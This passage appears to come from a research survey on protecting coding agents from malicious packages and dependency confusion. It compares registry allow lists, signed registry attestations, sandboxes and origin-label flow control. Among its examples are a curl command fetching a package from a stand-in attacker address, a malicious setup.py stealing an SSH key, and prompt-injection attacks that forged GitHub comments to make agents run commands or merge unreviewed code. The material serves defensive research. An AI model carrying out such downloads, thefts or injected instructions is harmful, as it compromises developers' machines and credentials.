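A registry allow list limits where packages can come from. Bagmar and Saraf propose varying the agent's response by source. The agent would install from PyPI with a warning about known vulnerabilities, and install without comment from private registries that the developer has configured. It would block an unknown registry until the developer confirms it, and refuse unencrypted sources. The harness would have to expand requirements files before applying the list. Bagmar and Saraf say that no current agent or package manager has such a scheme built in.

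Preventing dependency confusion requires one more rule, because the allow list may include both the public and internal registries. The developer has to reserve internal package names for the internal registry, so that the package manager never compares version numbers across the two. npm supports this through scopes, which are prefixes such as `@acme` that a settings file can tie to one registry. NuGet, the package manager for Microsoft's .NET, has let developers map name patterns to sources since 2022.

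McCann (2026), in *Cryptographic Registry Provenance*, objects that these protections are all settings that fail silently. If the line that ties `@acme` to the company's registry is missing, or a variable on the build machine overrides it, the installation still succeeds. Nothing in the installed package shows which registry it came from, so nobody can find the mistake by looking at the files afterwards.

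### Signed records of distribution

McCann's remedy is to attach to each package proof of which registry accepted it. Each publisher and each registry has a private key for signing and a public key that anyone can use to check the signature. The publisher writes and signs a manifest B, which contains the package's name, version, dependencies and a hash (a short digital fingerprint) of its files. When the registry receives the package, it checks the signature, recomputes the hash and confirms that the publisher may use the namespace, a prefix such as `@acme`. It then writes and signs an attestation A, which contains its own identity, the hash of B, the package's name and version, and the time of acceptance.

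The developer's project file says that `@acme` belongs to the company's registry and stores the fingerprint of that registry's public key. Before unpacking a package from `@acme`, the client requires that

- the publisher's signature on B is valid
- the registry's signature on A is valid
- the fingerprint of the key that signed A equals the stored fingerprint
- A names the namespace `@acme`.

After unpacking, the client recomputes the hash of the files and compares it with the one in B. Suppose an attacker gets `@acme/utils` version 9.0 onto the public registry, and a faulty setting sends the client there. The package carries the public registry's signature and its fingerprint doesn't match, so the client rejects it whatever its version number.

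The signatures that npm and PyPI already support identify the publisher or the build system. McCann points out that a package uploaded to two registries carries the same signature on both, so the signature can't reveal that one registry was substituted for the other. Of the eight package systems McCann compares, NuGet comes closest to solving this, with an optional registry signature that its client doesn't enforce by default.

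McCann also offers a proof that dependency confusion is impossible for a protected namespace if nobody steals the registry's key. The proof treats the signature check as independent of the developer's settings, but the stored fingerprint is in the same project file as those settings, so anyone who can edit the file can replace the fingerprint. McCann recommends keeping fingerprints in a separate protected file, and the proof holds only if developers do this. The condition matters more with coding agents, because they routinely edit project files and a stranger's repository comes with its own project file.

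The paper is also inconsistent about when the client checks the registry's signature. In one passage the client checks it on every installation, and in another only in a strict mode. The protection depends on checking every time. Checking a small package took a median of about one to two milliseconds, so speed is no reason to skip it. McCann built the system for Mashin, a platform for AI workflows, and assessed its security by analysis, without staging attacks. A valid record would prove only where a package came from, and a typosquatted package can have one.

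### Confining whatever runs

Checks before installation cannot catch malicious code in a package whose name, source and version are all as intended. Confinement is meant for that case. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* states that code an agent generates can use whatever files, credentials and network its environment provides. With confinement, the developer therefore decides in advance what the environment provides.

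CompGuard, which Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Compositional Exploits in Autonomous Coding Agents*, describe, is a detailed example. Half of it tracks where data came from, and the other half is a sandbox that the Linux kernel enforces. The sandbox uses Landlock, a feature with which a process gives up access to files for itself and everything it starts, and seccomp, which filters system calls. By default a tool gets the following access:

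| Resource | Access |
|---|---|
| The project folder, apart from git's hooks and settings | Read and write |
| A scratch folder | Read and write |
| System programs, installed packages, shell start-up files, git's hooks and settings | Read only |
| SSH keys and cloud credentials | None, unless the developer's policy grants it |
| Network | Only through a local proxy, to domains declared for that tool |

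Each tool call gets a new process with cleaned environment variables. When the call ends, CompGuard kills that process and its descendants, so a background program cannot outlive the command that started it, which was possible under Tether.

Under these rules, a `setup.py` cannot open an SSH key, and the proxy stops it from contacting an unlisted server. Unlike in the tested version of ActPlane, the order of these attempts doesn't matter. But the default rules also make installed packages read-only, so an ordinary pip installation could not finish. The developer would have to grant wider access for installation, the step that malicious packages exploit.

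Shah and Kathrotia did not test malicious packages. Their attacks chain harmless tools, as when one tool checks a settings file and writes a report that includes a password, and a second posts the report to a website. They ran 35 tasks for each of eight kinds of harm, with Gemini 3.5 Flash as the agent:

| Harm | Attacks that succeeded without protection | With CompGuard | Half that the authors credit |
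|---|---|---|---|
| Credentials sent out | 94.3% | 2.9% | Tracking |
| Hostile git hook installed | 97.1% | 3.1% | Sandbox |
| Shell command injected | 57.1% | 0% | Sandbox |
| Database or settings files overwritten | 94.3% | 0% | Sandbox |
| Build pipeline altered | 97.1% | 0% | Tracking |
| Encryption checks turned off | 100% | 0% | Tracking |
| Database privileges raised | 94.3% | 0% | Tracking |
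| Data sent through a hidden tunnel | 5.7% | 0% | Sandbox |

The two non-zero results under CompGuard each come from a single run in which a tool wrote a little data before the system killed it. No data left the machine or survived the clean-up in either run.

The last column matters most for the argument against flow tracking, and it supports that argument less than the totals do. Shah and Kathrotia credit the sandbox with stopping four of the eight harms, but the unprotected agent hardly ever managed one of those four, the hidden tunnel. They credit tracking with stopping the agent from sending out credentials, which is the usual aim of a malicious package. They didn't publish a run with the sandbox alone, so this division rests on their account of which component stopped each harm. They did test a filter on command text without the sandbox, and on average 66.9% of attacks still succeeded.

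CompGuard interfered little with the agent's work. On 100 harmless tasks that used the same tools, the protected agent completed 98 and the unprotected one 91. The difference comes from nine runs in which the unprotected agent ran out of turns. Shah and Kathrotia attribute this to pointless detours, which the sandbox cut short for the protected agent. CompGuard raised no false alarms in 615 diagnostic calls on recorded cloud failures, and it added about 61 microseconds to each tool call. These results come from the designers' own benchmarks, which used a fixed set of tools with permissions declared in advance, whereas a build script from an unknown package comes with no such declaration.

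### Sandboxes that developers already use

One practical advantage of confinement over flow control is that the large developers of coding agents already ship it. Anthropic first asked Claude Code's users to approve each risky action, and found that they approved about 93% of the requests and paid less attention as the number grew. It then added a sandbox in which the agent may read files and write inside the project folder, but has no network access by default. Permission requests fell by 84%. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's product for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that contains only the folders the user has chosen, and keeps the user's credentials outside it.

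Anthropic reports that Claude Code's Auto Mode misses about 17% of the overeager actions it is meant to stop. The company therefore treats it as an extra layer inside a sandbox, not as a replacement for one.

Codex has similar defaults, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. On a developer's machine, commands may write only to the project folder and temporary directories, cannot change git's data or Codex's own settings, and have no network access. A developer who turns the network on can restrict it to a list of allowed domains, which starts empty. OpenAI (2026) describes stricter rules for its own staff, who cannot switch the sandbox off. A central policy allows expected destinations, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. The boundary is deterministic, but a second model can grant some of these approvals, so the exceptions partly depend on a model's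 judgement.

These defaults matter when interpreting the agents' poor results against bad registries. In the poisoned pip settings scenario, Bagmar and Saraf gave Codex full access so that it could reach the test registry. With the network off, Codex would have had to ask the developer for permission first. The developer would then have had to make the decision that the agent got wrong, based only on the command and the request.

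Codex's cloud version installs dependencies in a setup phase with network access, and the agent then works offline by default. Secrets that the developer has configured are available during setup and removed before the agent starts. This protects them from the agent and from any prompt injection it reads, but not from install-time code, which runs while both the secrets and the network are available. Downloading and installing packages before any secret enters the container would be safer against package attacks, where the project allows it. None of the documents from Anthropic or OpenAI reports a test with malicious packages.

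### Two uploads to the same address

Supporters of flow control can accept all of these measures and still object that a fixed allow list checks only where an upload goes, not what it contains. A developer who wants an agent to publish open-source code has to allow the code-hosting site, and that permission also lets the agent upload a private key there.

Anthropic encountered this problem in Claude Cowork, where an outside researcher showed that files could leave the sandbox through a domain on the approved list, even though the sandbox was working as designed. Anthropic now describes an entry on such a list as a "capability grant", because the entry permits everything the domain offers. Anthropic fixed the problem with a proxy that also checks whose account a request uses. This works for one service, whose requests Anthropic understood in detail, but a developer would need a comparable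 rule for every other service on the list.

The CompGuard benchmark has the same problem, because each harmless task uses tools that also appear in the attacks. In one pair, the same tool posts test-coverage figures to the messaging service Slack in the harmless version and database passwords in the attack, so a list of approved tools would have to allow both or block both. CompGuard told them apart by tracking where the data came from. It still raised false alarms on 10% of the harmless tasks when Shah and Kathrotia labelled whole settings files as secret, but labelling individual entries reduced this to 2%.

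Confinement can protect a secret by keeping it outside the sandbox. This is often enough for SSH keys, but it doesn't work for data that the agent needs for its task. For example, an agent that moves a bug fix from a company's private repository to its public one must be able to read the private code and upload to the public site. No sandbox setting can allow it to upload the fix but block it from uploading the rest of the private code.

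## Whether origin labels stop dependency confusion and related attacks

Nobody appears to have published an experiment that tests flow control against malicious packages. The tests of FIDES, ELBA and ActPlane include no such packages. The closest research uses flow analysis to detect malicious code and leaves blocking to other tools. *Taint-Based Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection* (2025) applies taint analysis to npm packages, and *NodeShield* (2025) cites RogueOne, which detects rogue package updates by comparing data flows.

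*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) uses TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios from 20 open-source agent frameworks, to test whether a monitor can tell that an attacker's text has reached or influenced a tool call with side effects. The text does so in half of the scenarios. Such a test would miss dependency confusion, because none of the attacker's text has to reach the install command. *AgenticOS* (2026) proposes an operating system for agents and lists source labels among its measures against supply-chain poisoning, with checks at outputs such as uploads and messages.

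This section therefore derives the effect of labels on package attacks from the rules of the design below. The design takes its parts from published systems, but nobody has measured its results.

### Why two levels fail

Suppose a company, Acme, keeps version 1.2.0 of a package named `acme-auth` on its internal registry. An attacker learns the name and publishes version 99.0.0 under the same name on the public registry. McCann lists several places where such names leak, including lockfiles, build logs and error messages. A developer at Acme then asks a coding agent to install the dependencies of a project whose `requirements.txt` lists `acme-auth` and `requests`, a popular public library. Pip's settings include both registries, so pip chooses the attacker's package because it has the higher version number.

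In the lattice with only T and U, files from the internal registry get the label T. The public registry needs a label too, and neither choice works:

| Label of the public registry | Impostor `acme-auth` 99.0.0 | Genuine `requests` |
|---|---|---|
| T | Installed | Installed |
| U | Blocked | Blocked |

The impostor and `requests` come from the same server. If a file's label depends only on its server, both files have the same label, and an install sink with one limit must accept both or refuse both. Adding more levels doesn't change this. The developer could endorse `requests` and every other public package individually, but then the list of endorsed names, rather than the labels, would determine which packages can be installed.

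Labelling the command doesn't help either. The developer's request and the company's requirements file are both T, so `pip install -r requirements.txt` is T too. A trusted-action policy like the one in FIDES correctly lets it run, since no attacker influenced the command. The attacker influences the install later, when pip queries the registries for available versions. The version number 99.0.0 is untrusted data that determines which file pip downloads. This is an implicit flow, and it happens inside a program that the harness treats as a single step.

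### Labels that name their origins

A more informative label is a set of origins. Costa and colleagues describe an integrity label that lists everyone who could have written the data. Labels in ELBA, the system by Zhou and colleagues, can also include web domains. When a program fetches a page, ELBA adds the page's domain to the program's label and then blocks the program from writing to any sink reserved for the user's own data.

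Seven origins are enough for the Acme example:

| Origin | What it covers |
|---|---|
| owner | The developer's request, and settings that the agent cannot change |
| manifest | The project's list of dependencies, as a person last reviewed it |
| text | READMEs, source code, web pages and the output of commands |
| model | Anything the language model writes |
| internal | The company's registry |
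| public | The public registry |
| other | Any other server |

As in ActPlane, A ≤ B means A ⊆ B, and the join of A and B is A ∪ B. Seven origins give 2⁷ = 128 possible labels. The two-level lattice is a coarser version in which someone picks the trusted origins and gives the label T to data whose origins are all trusted.

Grouping all ordinary text together has a precedent in *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), which describes a harness that treats READMEs, agent instruction files, skill files and tool output as untrusted. The model needs its own origin because FIDES gives a model's reply the label of whatever the model has read. If the model had read only the developer's request and then invented a package name, that name would get the label {owner}, as if the developer had typed it.

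ActPlane could store these labels easily, since each origin needs one bit of its 64-bit mask. It could not give every package its own bit, because an average npm package implicitly trusts 79 others, according to *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (2026).

### Three labels and three rules

Each package p that pip might install gets three labels:

- N(p), the origins of the text that supplied its name
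- A(p), the origins of the setting that supplied the registry's address
- F(p), the servers that the file came through

The name and address labels have to stay separate until the check is over, because joining them hides which source supplied the address. The joined label would be {owner, manifest} in the normal case, where the manifest supplies the name and the owner supplies the address. It would be the same if the developer's request supplied the name and the manifest supplied the address, and a hidden registry gets in through an address in the manifest.

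The harness accepts a package only if it satisfies all three of these rules:

| Rule | Condition |
|---|---|
| Name rule | N(p) ⊆ {owner, manifest, internal, public} |
| Address rule | A(p) ⊆ {owner} |
| Binding rule | F(p) ⊆ B(p) |

The name rule includes the two registries because the harness would otherwise refuse every indirect dependency. If `acme-auth` requires another package, for example, that package's name comes from the internal registry's metadata and has the label {manifest, internal}.

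B(p) is the set of servers that may supply a package named p. For Acme, B(`acme-auth`) = {internal} and B(`requests`) = {internal, public}. The binding rule has the same form as any other flow rule, label(data) ≤ label(sink), except that each package name is now a sink with its own limit. These per-name limits, which the two-level lattice lacked, allow the harness to refuse one public file while accepting another.

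An agent usually reads the README before it writes an install command, so a package name in that command would have the label {owner, text, model} and fail the name rule. The harness can endorse the name by changing its label to {manifest} if exactly the same name is in the reviewed manifest, or to {owner} if it is in the developer's request. The README may still have influenced the agent's choice, but at worst the attacker gets the agent to install something that the project or the developer has already named. Names that the agent adds to the manifest keep their old labels until someone reviews them, because otherwise the agent could make any name trusted by writing it to `requirements.txt`.

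### The impostor, step by step

The check has to come after pip has found the available files, because F(p) doesn't exist before then, and before any package code runs. This fits the advice of Bagmar and Saraf that a production check should examine the resolved packages instead of the command. For Acme's project it works as follows:

| Step | Label | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| The harness finds both names in the reviewed manifest | N = {manifest} | Passes the name rule |
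| Pip takes both registry addresses from the company's settings | A = {owner} | Passes the address rule |
| The public registry offers `acme-auth` 99.0.0 | F = {public} | {public} ⊄ {internal}, so the harness discards it |
| The internal registry offers `acme-auth` 1.2.0 | F = {internal} | {internal} ⊆ {internal}, so it stays |
| The public registry offers `requests` | F = {public} | {public} ⊆ {internal, public}, so it stays |
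| Pip chooses the highest versions that remain | | `acme-auth` 1.2.0 and the latest `requests` |
| The installed files take the union N ∪ A ∪ F | {owner, manifest, internal} and {owner, manifest, public} | Install-time code may run |

The harness discards the impostor before pip compares versions. If pip chose a package first and the harness then rejected it, the attacker's code would not run, but the genuine package would not be installed either. Anyone could then stop Acme's builds by publishing a package with the same name and a higher version number. A local proxy between pip and the registries could remove the forbidden files from the list that pip receives.

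The proxy would also show where each file actually came from, which is safer than reading the origin from a lockfile. Bos describes a lockfile entry with two addresses for the same package. Yarn, a JavaScript package manager, uses the last one, so a checker that used the first would label the file {public} while Yarn downloaded it from the attacker's server.

Some Python packages come only as source code, and pip may have to run their build code just to determine their dependencies. The harness would have to either accept only prebuilt packages at this stage or restrict the build code as described below.

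Confidentiality labels can also stop the impostor. Acme can label the name `acme-auth` as secret and permit only the internal registry to receive it. This rule blocks pip from querying the public registry for versions of `acme-auth`, so pip never finds version 99.0.0. It also prevents the query from revealing the name to outsiders. Each name needs its own label, however, because if the whole requirements file were secret, pip could not query the public registry for `requests` either.

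### If the impostor gets through

This works only if Acme has listed `acme-auth` as an internal name. Otherwise, the name gets the default set {internal, public}, and version 99.0.0 passes the check. A second barrier then has to limit what the package's code can do.

Suppose the operating system gives every process a set of origins and a confidentiality label, and spreads both in the way ActPlane spreads its labels. Two more rules apply to any process whose origins include a registry or another server:

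- The secrets rule: the process may use the network only while its confidentiality label is L.
- The write rule: the process may write only to a temporary folder and to the project's environment, the folder that holds the project's installed packages.

The write rule is ordinary confinement. *Security Issues in Language-based Software Ecosystems* (2019) suggested restricting installation scripts to a given directory. The secrets rule does use the labels. Suppose the impostor's `setup.py` tries to steal an SSH key:

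| Event | Process label | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Pip runs `setup.py` | ({owner, manifest, public}, L) | Allowed |
| `setup.py` reads the SSH key | ({owner, manifest, public}, H) | Allowed |
| It connects to the attacker's server | Unchanged | Blocked by the secrets rule |
| It adds a command to the shell's start-up file | Unchanged | Blocked by the write rule |
| It hides the key in an installed module | Unchanged | Allowed, and the module takes the process's label |
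| A test program imports the module the next day | Includes public and H | Allowed, but the program cannot use the network |

A sandbox that cut off the network only during installation would miss the delayed theft in the last two rows. The secrets rule catches it because the module is now H, as is any program that imports it. A deployment tool can still read a key and send it if the developer starts the tool and it loads no package code. The rule follows robust declassification, since code from a registry cannot decide which secrets leave the machine. The system must check the labels each time a process sends data, as ContractWarden does. Otherwise, the script could open a connection before reading the key, then send the key over it.

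The second barrier would therefore protect the developer's key, shell settings and other projects. It would not stop the impostor from sending the machine's name, or source code that nobody had labelled H. Environment variables are a more serious gap, because a process receives them when it starts, without opening a file that would change its label. In Bagmar and Saraf's tests, the agent's process inherited the developer's full environment, including API keys and cloud credentials. The harness would have to remove these variables before installation, or start the process at H and keep it offline throughout.

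The rules also protect only the machine that enforces them. The impostor package remains in the project's environment, and if the developer ships it with the product, its code will run on customers' machines without labels.

### Keeping ordinary programs working

Pip could break the secrets rule during a legitimate installation. If the internal registry requires a password, pip reads a secret, and once it has also read a file from the public registry, the rule stops it from making further connections. The harness can solve this by splitting the installation into two processes. One downloads the files with the password and never runs package code, so the harness can exempt it from the rule. The other runs the install-time code without access to the password.

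Running the code in an ordinary sandbox with no network and no secrets would give about the same protection without labels. The secrets rule is more permissive. Bos notes that some installation scripts fetch additional resources, and the rule would still allow this if the scripts had not read a secret. This difference may affect few packages, at least on npm, where *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* cites a finding that only 2.2% of packages declare installation scripts.

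The harness must also limit how labels travel back to the agent. In *Agent-Warden*, a parent process takes on the mark of a child that exits, which helps investigators trace short-lived programs. With the secrets rule in place, the same design would add the public registry to the agent's own label after one installation, and if the agent's process then read a secret, it could no longer contact the model that runs it. Agent-Warden only records events, so an unnecessary mark blocks nothing. A system that blocks actions would need to pass labels to child processes and files but not automatically to the parent.

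The secrets rule is hardest to apply when the finished program runs. A web application typically reads a database password, connects to the database and imports many public packages, all in one process. That process's label would include both the public registry and H, so the rule would block the database connection.

More precise tracking inside the program could in principle separate the password from the packages. *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System* (2021) rejects this approach because static analysis of JavaScript is too imprecise and tracking data while the program runs often slows it by a factor of 40 to 100. The paper proposes permissions for each package instead.

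Ohm, Pohl and Boes (2023), in *You Can Run But You Can't Hide*, tested a similar approach, which automatically limits each Node.js package to the capabilities it needs. It prevented nine of ten historic attacks and added a median delay of less than 0.2 seconds at runtime. The test was small, but it used real attacks, and flow control has no comparable result. The approach is also designed for malicious updates, which pass every origin check.

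### Other attacks under the same rules

The rules give different results for the other attacks. The table assumes the company's own settings supply the registry address unless the attack changes it. The last column gives a check that needs no labels.

| Attack | Name label | Address label | File label | Result before installation | Ordinary check that can block it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Dependency confusion | manifest | owner | public | Blocked by the binding rule | Reserved internal names |
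| Hidden registry in the requirements file | manifest | manifest | other | Blocked by the address and binding rules | Registry allow list |
| Typosquat only in the README | text, model | owner | public | Blocked by the name rule | Refusal of undeclared packages |
| Typosquat in the manifest | manifest | owner | public | Passes | Comparison with known names |
| Name invented by the model | owner, model | owner | public | Blocked by the name rule | Refusal of undeclared packages |
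| Package named in an error message | text, model | owner | public | Blocked by the name rule | Refusal of undeclared packages |
| Vulnerable version | manifest | owner | public | Passes | Vulnerability database |
| Compromised maintainer | manifest | owner | public | Passes | Lockfile that fixes an earlier version |
| Malicious indirect dependency | manifest, public | owner | public | Passes | Review of the lockfile, if the reviewer recognises the threat |

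The binding rule also stops an attack that Bagmar and Saraf's hook would allow. Once the developer had approved an extra registry for one package, `httpclient`, the hook would accept a poisoned `pytest` from the same registry, and the address rule would no longer block the registry either. With origin labels, the developer can give the registry its own origin, `partner`, and set B(`httpclient`) = {partner}. The poisoned `pytest` has the file label {partner}, which is not a subset of {internal, public}, so the harness discards it.

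A typosquat in the manifest has the same labels as a genuine package, because the attacker did publish it on the public registry and the project does list it. Only its name distinguishes it. *ConfuGuard* (2025) describes a system that detects confusing names and helped identify 301 confirmed threats in three months of use by an industry partner. A short list of common misspellings would catch fewer attacks. *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* cites a study that found 13 mechanisms of name confusion in 1,232 documented attacks, and typosquatting is only one of them.

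Whether origin labels stop invented names depends on who approves changes to the manifest. In a new project, the agent may write the whole list of dependencies. If the developer approves the list without looking up each name, an invented one gets the label {manifest} and passes from then on.

The name rule blocks the package in the error message because the project doesn't declare it. The agents used the same clue and, according to Bagmar and Saraf's transcripts, also noticed that a file already in the project satisfied the import.

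Bagmar and Saraf consider an installation secure if the package is authentic (it comes from a trusted source), intended (its name matches what the developer needs) and safe (the version has no known unpatched vulnerability). Origin labels mainly address authenticity. They help with intention when a package with the wrong name also comes from the wrong source. They don't help with safety, because a vulnerable version comes from the same maintainer and registry as a fixed one.

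Flow analysis can help judge how much a vulnerability matters. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) uses taint analysis to assess whether an agent's inputs can reach the vulnerable function in a dependency without passing an effective check. This requires analysis of the program's code, which the labels on an installation don't provide.

A compromised maintainer defeats the first barrier, because the package's name, address and file all match what the project specified. Such attacks spread quickly. Bagmar and Saraf cite the LiteLLM compromise of 2026, in which malicious versions were downloaded more than 119,000 times in under three hours. McCann cites the ua-parser-js case of 2021, in which an attacker took over the maintainer's account for a package with more than 7 million weekly downloads. A lockfile would have kept existing projects on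 their earlier versions. If a developer did install a malicious version, the second barrier would still restrict it as it would the impostor's code.

### What an allow list could do alone

The binding rule stops dependency confusion, but in the simplest case it hardly uses the lattice. If a file comes directly from one server, F(p) has one member, and the test F(p) ⊆ B(p) is a table lookup of a name and a registry. An allow list of permitted name and registry pairs, which npm's scopes and NuGet's source mappings already offer developers, would refuse the impostor just as reliably. The address rule gives the same result as a fixed list of registries, and the name rule gives the same result as refusing to install undeclared packages.

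The lattice becomes useful when a file passes through several servers on its way to pip. Many companies run a proxy that serves both their own packages and public ones from one address. An allow list that checks only this address would accept the impostor even if the proxy had fetched it from the public registry. An origin label records both servers, so the impostor has the label {internal, public}. The binding rule refuses it because this label is not a subset of {internal}. The same label is acceptable for `requests`. The proxy must report where it got each file, or the harness will label the impostor {internal} and let it through.

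An attacker can also avoid registries altogether. A README could tell the agent to download a file from a website and install it from the project folder:

```
curl -o acme_auth.whl <attacker's address>    # file gets the label {other}
mv acme_auth.whl packages/                    # label stays with the file
pip install packages/acme_auth.whl            # {other} is not within {internal}
```

In practice the file would need a longer name, because pip reads the version from the filename, but the labels would be the same. A registry allow list would not stop this attack, because pip contacts no registry for this file. A rule against all local files would stop it, but would also stop the developer from installing the project's own code. The origin label distinguishes the malicious file from the project's code, provided the label stays with the file when the agent moves it. Agent-Warden's marks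 already survive renaming.

An attacker could describe this detour or a similar one in a line or two of a README. Nobody has tested whether coding agents follow such instructions as readily as they accepted bad registries, so it is unknown how much the lattice improves on an allow list. A direct test would run the same attacks twice, once with all the rules and once with only the table of names and registries.

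## Whether the labels themselves can be trusted

Flow control enforces rules about labels but doesn't check that the labels are correct. In the systems described so far, each source first gets its label from a developer who marks each tool, a server that labels the data it sends, or a default that applies when nobody chooses one. Every later label is a join of these initial labels, so a mistake in a source's label affects everything computed from that source.

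The designs assume that someone can sort sources into trusted and untrusted, that content from a trusted source is likely to be safe, and that the developer's request and the agent's own output can be trusted. Attacks and measurements from 2026 show how each assumption can fail.

### One repository, many authors

A repository's contents come from many people. The owner writes some files, contributors send pull requests (proposed code changes), strangers open issues, and anyone on the team may paste in code from a website. GitHub's server for Copilot, in the experimental setting described earlier, can give all of this the same label, based on whether the repository is public or private. Code that an employee copied from a forum into a private repository then counts as trusted, while the owner's build script in a public repository counts as untrusted.

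Git's history would allow finer labels, but it records who committed a line, not where that person got it. If the owner pastes 40 lines from a forum, git attributes them to the owner. Similarly, GitHub's integrity gateway gives code from merged pull requests its highest trust level, which makes sense only if someone read the code before merging it.

Labels based on a file's location can also be wrong. *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector* (Trent, 2026) describes malware from the Shai-Hulud family of npm worms that adds its own start-up commands to Claude Code's settings. A harness that trusts the settings folder because it belongs to the developer would accept those commands. An operating system that passes labels from processes to the files they write would instead label the changed settings with the malicious package's origin.

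### Forged authors inside a tool result

Coarse labels cause particular trouble when one tool result mixes facts supplied by a service with text written by strangers. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes attacks that exploit this mixture. A GitHub issue, for example, reaches the model as a list of comments, each with an author, a role and a body. GitHub supplies the author and role, but the commenter writes the body. An attacker can write a body that imitates the format of the list, so that the model mistakes part of it for a separate comment by a maintainer. A strict parser would keep the forged comment inside the body, but a language model interprets the format only approximately, so even an imperfect imitation can fool it.

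An attacker can exploit a task the developer has already given the agent. If the developer asks for the maintainer's fix, the agent tries to apply it but runs the attacker's command instead. This worked on Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI. In another attack on the same three agents, the description of a pull request was made to look like the record of an earlier tool call. The model treated the proposed code as already reviewed, and the agent merged it without reading it. GitHub's gateway would then give that code its highest trust level.

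Choi and colleagues also made three web-browsing agents click the wrong button by forging the identifiers of page elements. The attack failed against ChatGPT Atlas, which gives elements random identifiers that an attacker cannot easily predict.

To compare defences, the researchers added 108 data injections to AgentDojo and ran them against an agent based on GPT-5.2. They also ran the benchmark's 935 ordinary injections, which succeeded at most 0.7% of the time under any defence. The data injections did much better:

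| Defence | Data injections that succeeded |
|---|---|
| None beyond the model's own training | 49.1% |
| Classifier that looks for injected instructions | 50.0% |
| Model that checks actions against the user's request | 45.4% |
| Plan fixed before the agent reads any data | 40.7% |
| Random suffixes on field names | 28.7% |
| CaMeL without flow policies | 25.0% |
| CaMeL with normal flow tracking | 23.1% |
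| Progent, which restricts tool calls by policy | 22.2% |
| CaMeL with strict flow tracking | 0% |

CaMeL without policies keeps untrusted text away from the planner, but its quarantined model can still misread a forged field and return the attacker's value. Normal tracking should have marked that value as untrusted, but Choi and colleagues reported a bug that often dropped the label when the quarantined model extracted the value. The strict version also tracks implicit flows, so the difference between 23.1% and 0% doesn't show how much that tracking helped.

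The perfect score came with a large drop in harmless tasks completed, from 86.5% for the unprotected agent to 36.5% for CaMeL in strict mode. The test used simulated office, banking and travel tasks, so it doesn't measure how well flow tracking would protect a coding agent that reads GitHub issues.

Strict tracking can stop the attack because the label doesn't depend on how the model interprets the text. A command from a stranger's comment stays U even if the model attributes it to a maintainer. But the labels also have to be fine enough to let the maintainer's real command through. Suppose an issue contains one comment from a maintainer and one from a stranger who has forged a maintainer's name, and the shell accepts only T:

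| How the harness labels the issue | Maintainer's command | Stranger's command |
|---|---|---|
| One label for everything, T | Runs | Runs |
| One label for everything, U | Blocked | Blocked |
| Authors T, all comment bodies U | Blocked | Blocked |
| Each body according to its real author | Runs | Blocked |

Only the last policy does what the developer asked. To apply it, the harness has to read the author fields with an ordinary parser and store each comment separately before any model sees the text. If one model reads both comments together, its answer takes the join of their labels, which is U. The parser can separate the fields reliably if GitHub's command-line tool returns the issue as JSON, but not if it returns plain text, because a comment can then imitate the headings between comments.

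Choi and colleagues conclude that flow tracking can prevent these attacks only with a fine-grained policy. Such policies are hard to write because agents handle many kinds of data and actions. Tracking data closely enough also tends to make agents less useful, especially when they interpret large, unstructured documents such as web pages.

### Malicious releases with good credentials

Even a correct label of origin helps only if origin predicts safety. For packages, one of the best records of origin is provenance, a signed statement of which repository and automated workflow produced a release. Provenance is closely linked to trusted publishing, in which a registry accepts releases from a workflow the maintainer has registered, so the maintainer doesn't need to store a long-lived publishing token.

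Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *A Difference Without a Distinction*, measured how many regularly released packages carry signed provenance. On npm, 51.4% of popular packages and 25.9% of randomly chosen ones did, so a harness that trusted only packages with provenance would refuse about half of the popular ones. Of 188 packages that had ever published a stable release with provenance, 19 later published one without it.

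Missing provenance could still serve as a warning, because an attacker with a stolen token can publish without using the project's workflow. The package manager pnpm has an optional setting that refuses a release if an earlier release of the same package had stronger evidence. In Santos-Grueiro's tests, the setting prevented the installation of 16 of the 1,000 most popular npm packages and 76 of 997 recently updated ones. A single release, `semver` 6.3.1, caused 14 of the 16 failures. It was a security fix that a maintainer had published by hand.

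The setting can catch an attack on a package only if the package had such evidence beforehand. In the study, 17.5% of the 1,654 attacked packages did. The 95% interval is wide, from 6.5% to 43.9%, because a few large campaigns account for many of the packages.

Two cases show that this evidence is a weak guide to safety. In April 2026, the maintainers of `uuid` fixed the same vulnerability in three older versions. They published two of the fixes through their workflow and the third by hand, and pnpm refused the third. In March, an attacker who had taken over the `axios` lead maintainer's account published a malicious version, 0.30.4. The maintainers' own 0.30.3 came from the same account and also lacked provenance, so pnpm's rule could not distinguish the two releases.

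Attackers can also produce valid provenance. Santos-Grueiro counted 119 malicious versions of 46 packages that attackers published through the projects' own trusted publishers. In one case from September 2026, an attacker with access to a maintainer's account changed the release workflow and used it to publish malware, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Abuse npm Trusted Publishing in GHAPPIER Campaign*. The signed record correctly named the repository, the workflow and the attacker's commit.

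An attacker doesn't always need the maintainer's account. SLSA (2026), a project that develops standards for build provenance, describes an attack on TanStack, a family of JavaScript libraries, that began with a pull request from outside the project. An automated check ran the pull request's code, which tampered with a cache that the release workflow later used, much as in the Clinejection case. When the release workflow ran, the attacker's code took the workflow's identity token and published directly to npm.

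Origin labels let such releases through at installation. A more specific label identifying the publisher would not have stopped the releases that came through the projects' own workflows either.

### Names that change hands

A label can also be wrong about the origin itself. Help Net Security's *npm Trusted Publishing flaw exposed 1,500+ npm packages to takeover* (2026) reports a flaw that Bloom Security found in npm's trusted publishing. When a maintainer registered a workflow, npm stored the name of its GitHub repository. GitHub also gives every repository and owner a permanent number, but npm did not check these numbers, even though GitHub included them in the identity token it issued to the workflow.

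If the maintainer later renamed or deleted the repository, someone else could take the old name and publish new versions of the package. Bloom demonstrated this on its own package and counted more than 1,500 exposed packages, with over a million combined monthly downloads. A release published this way carried valid provenance because the workflow had run in the repository that now had that name.

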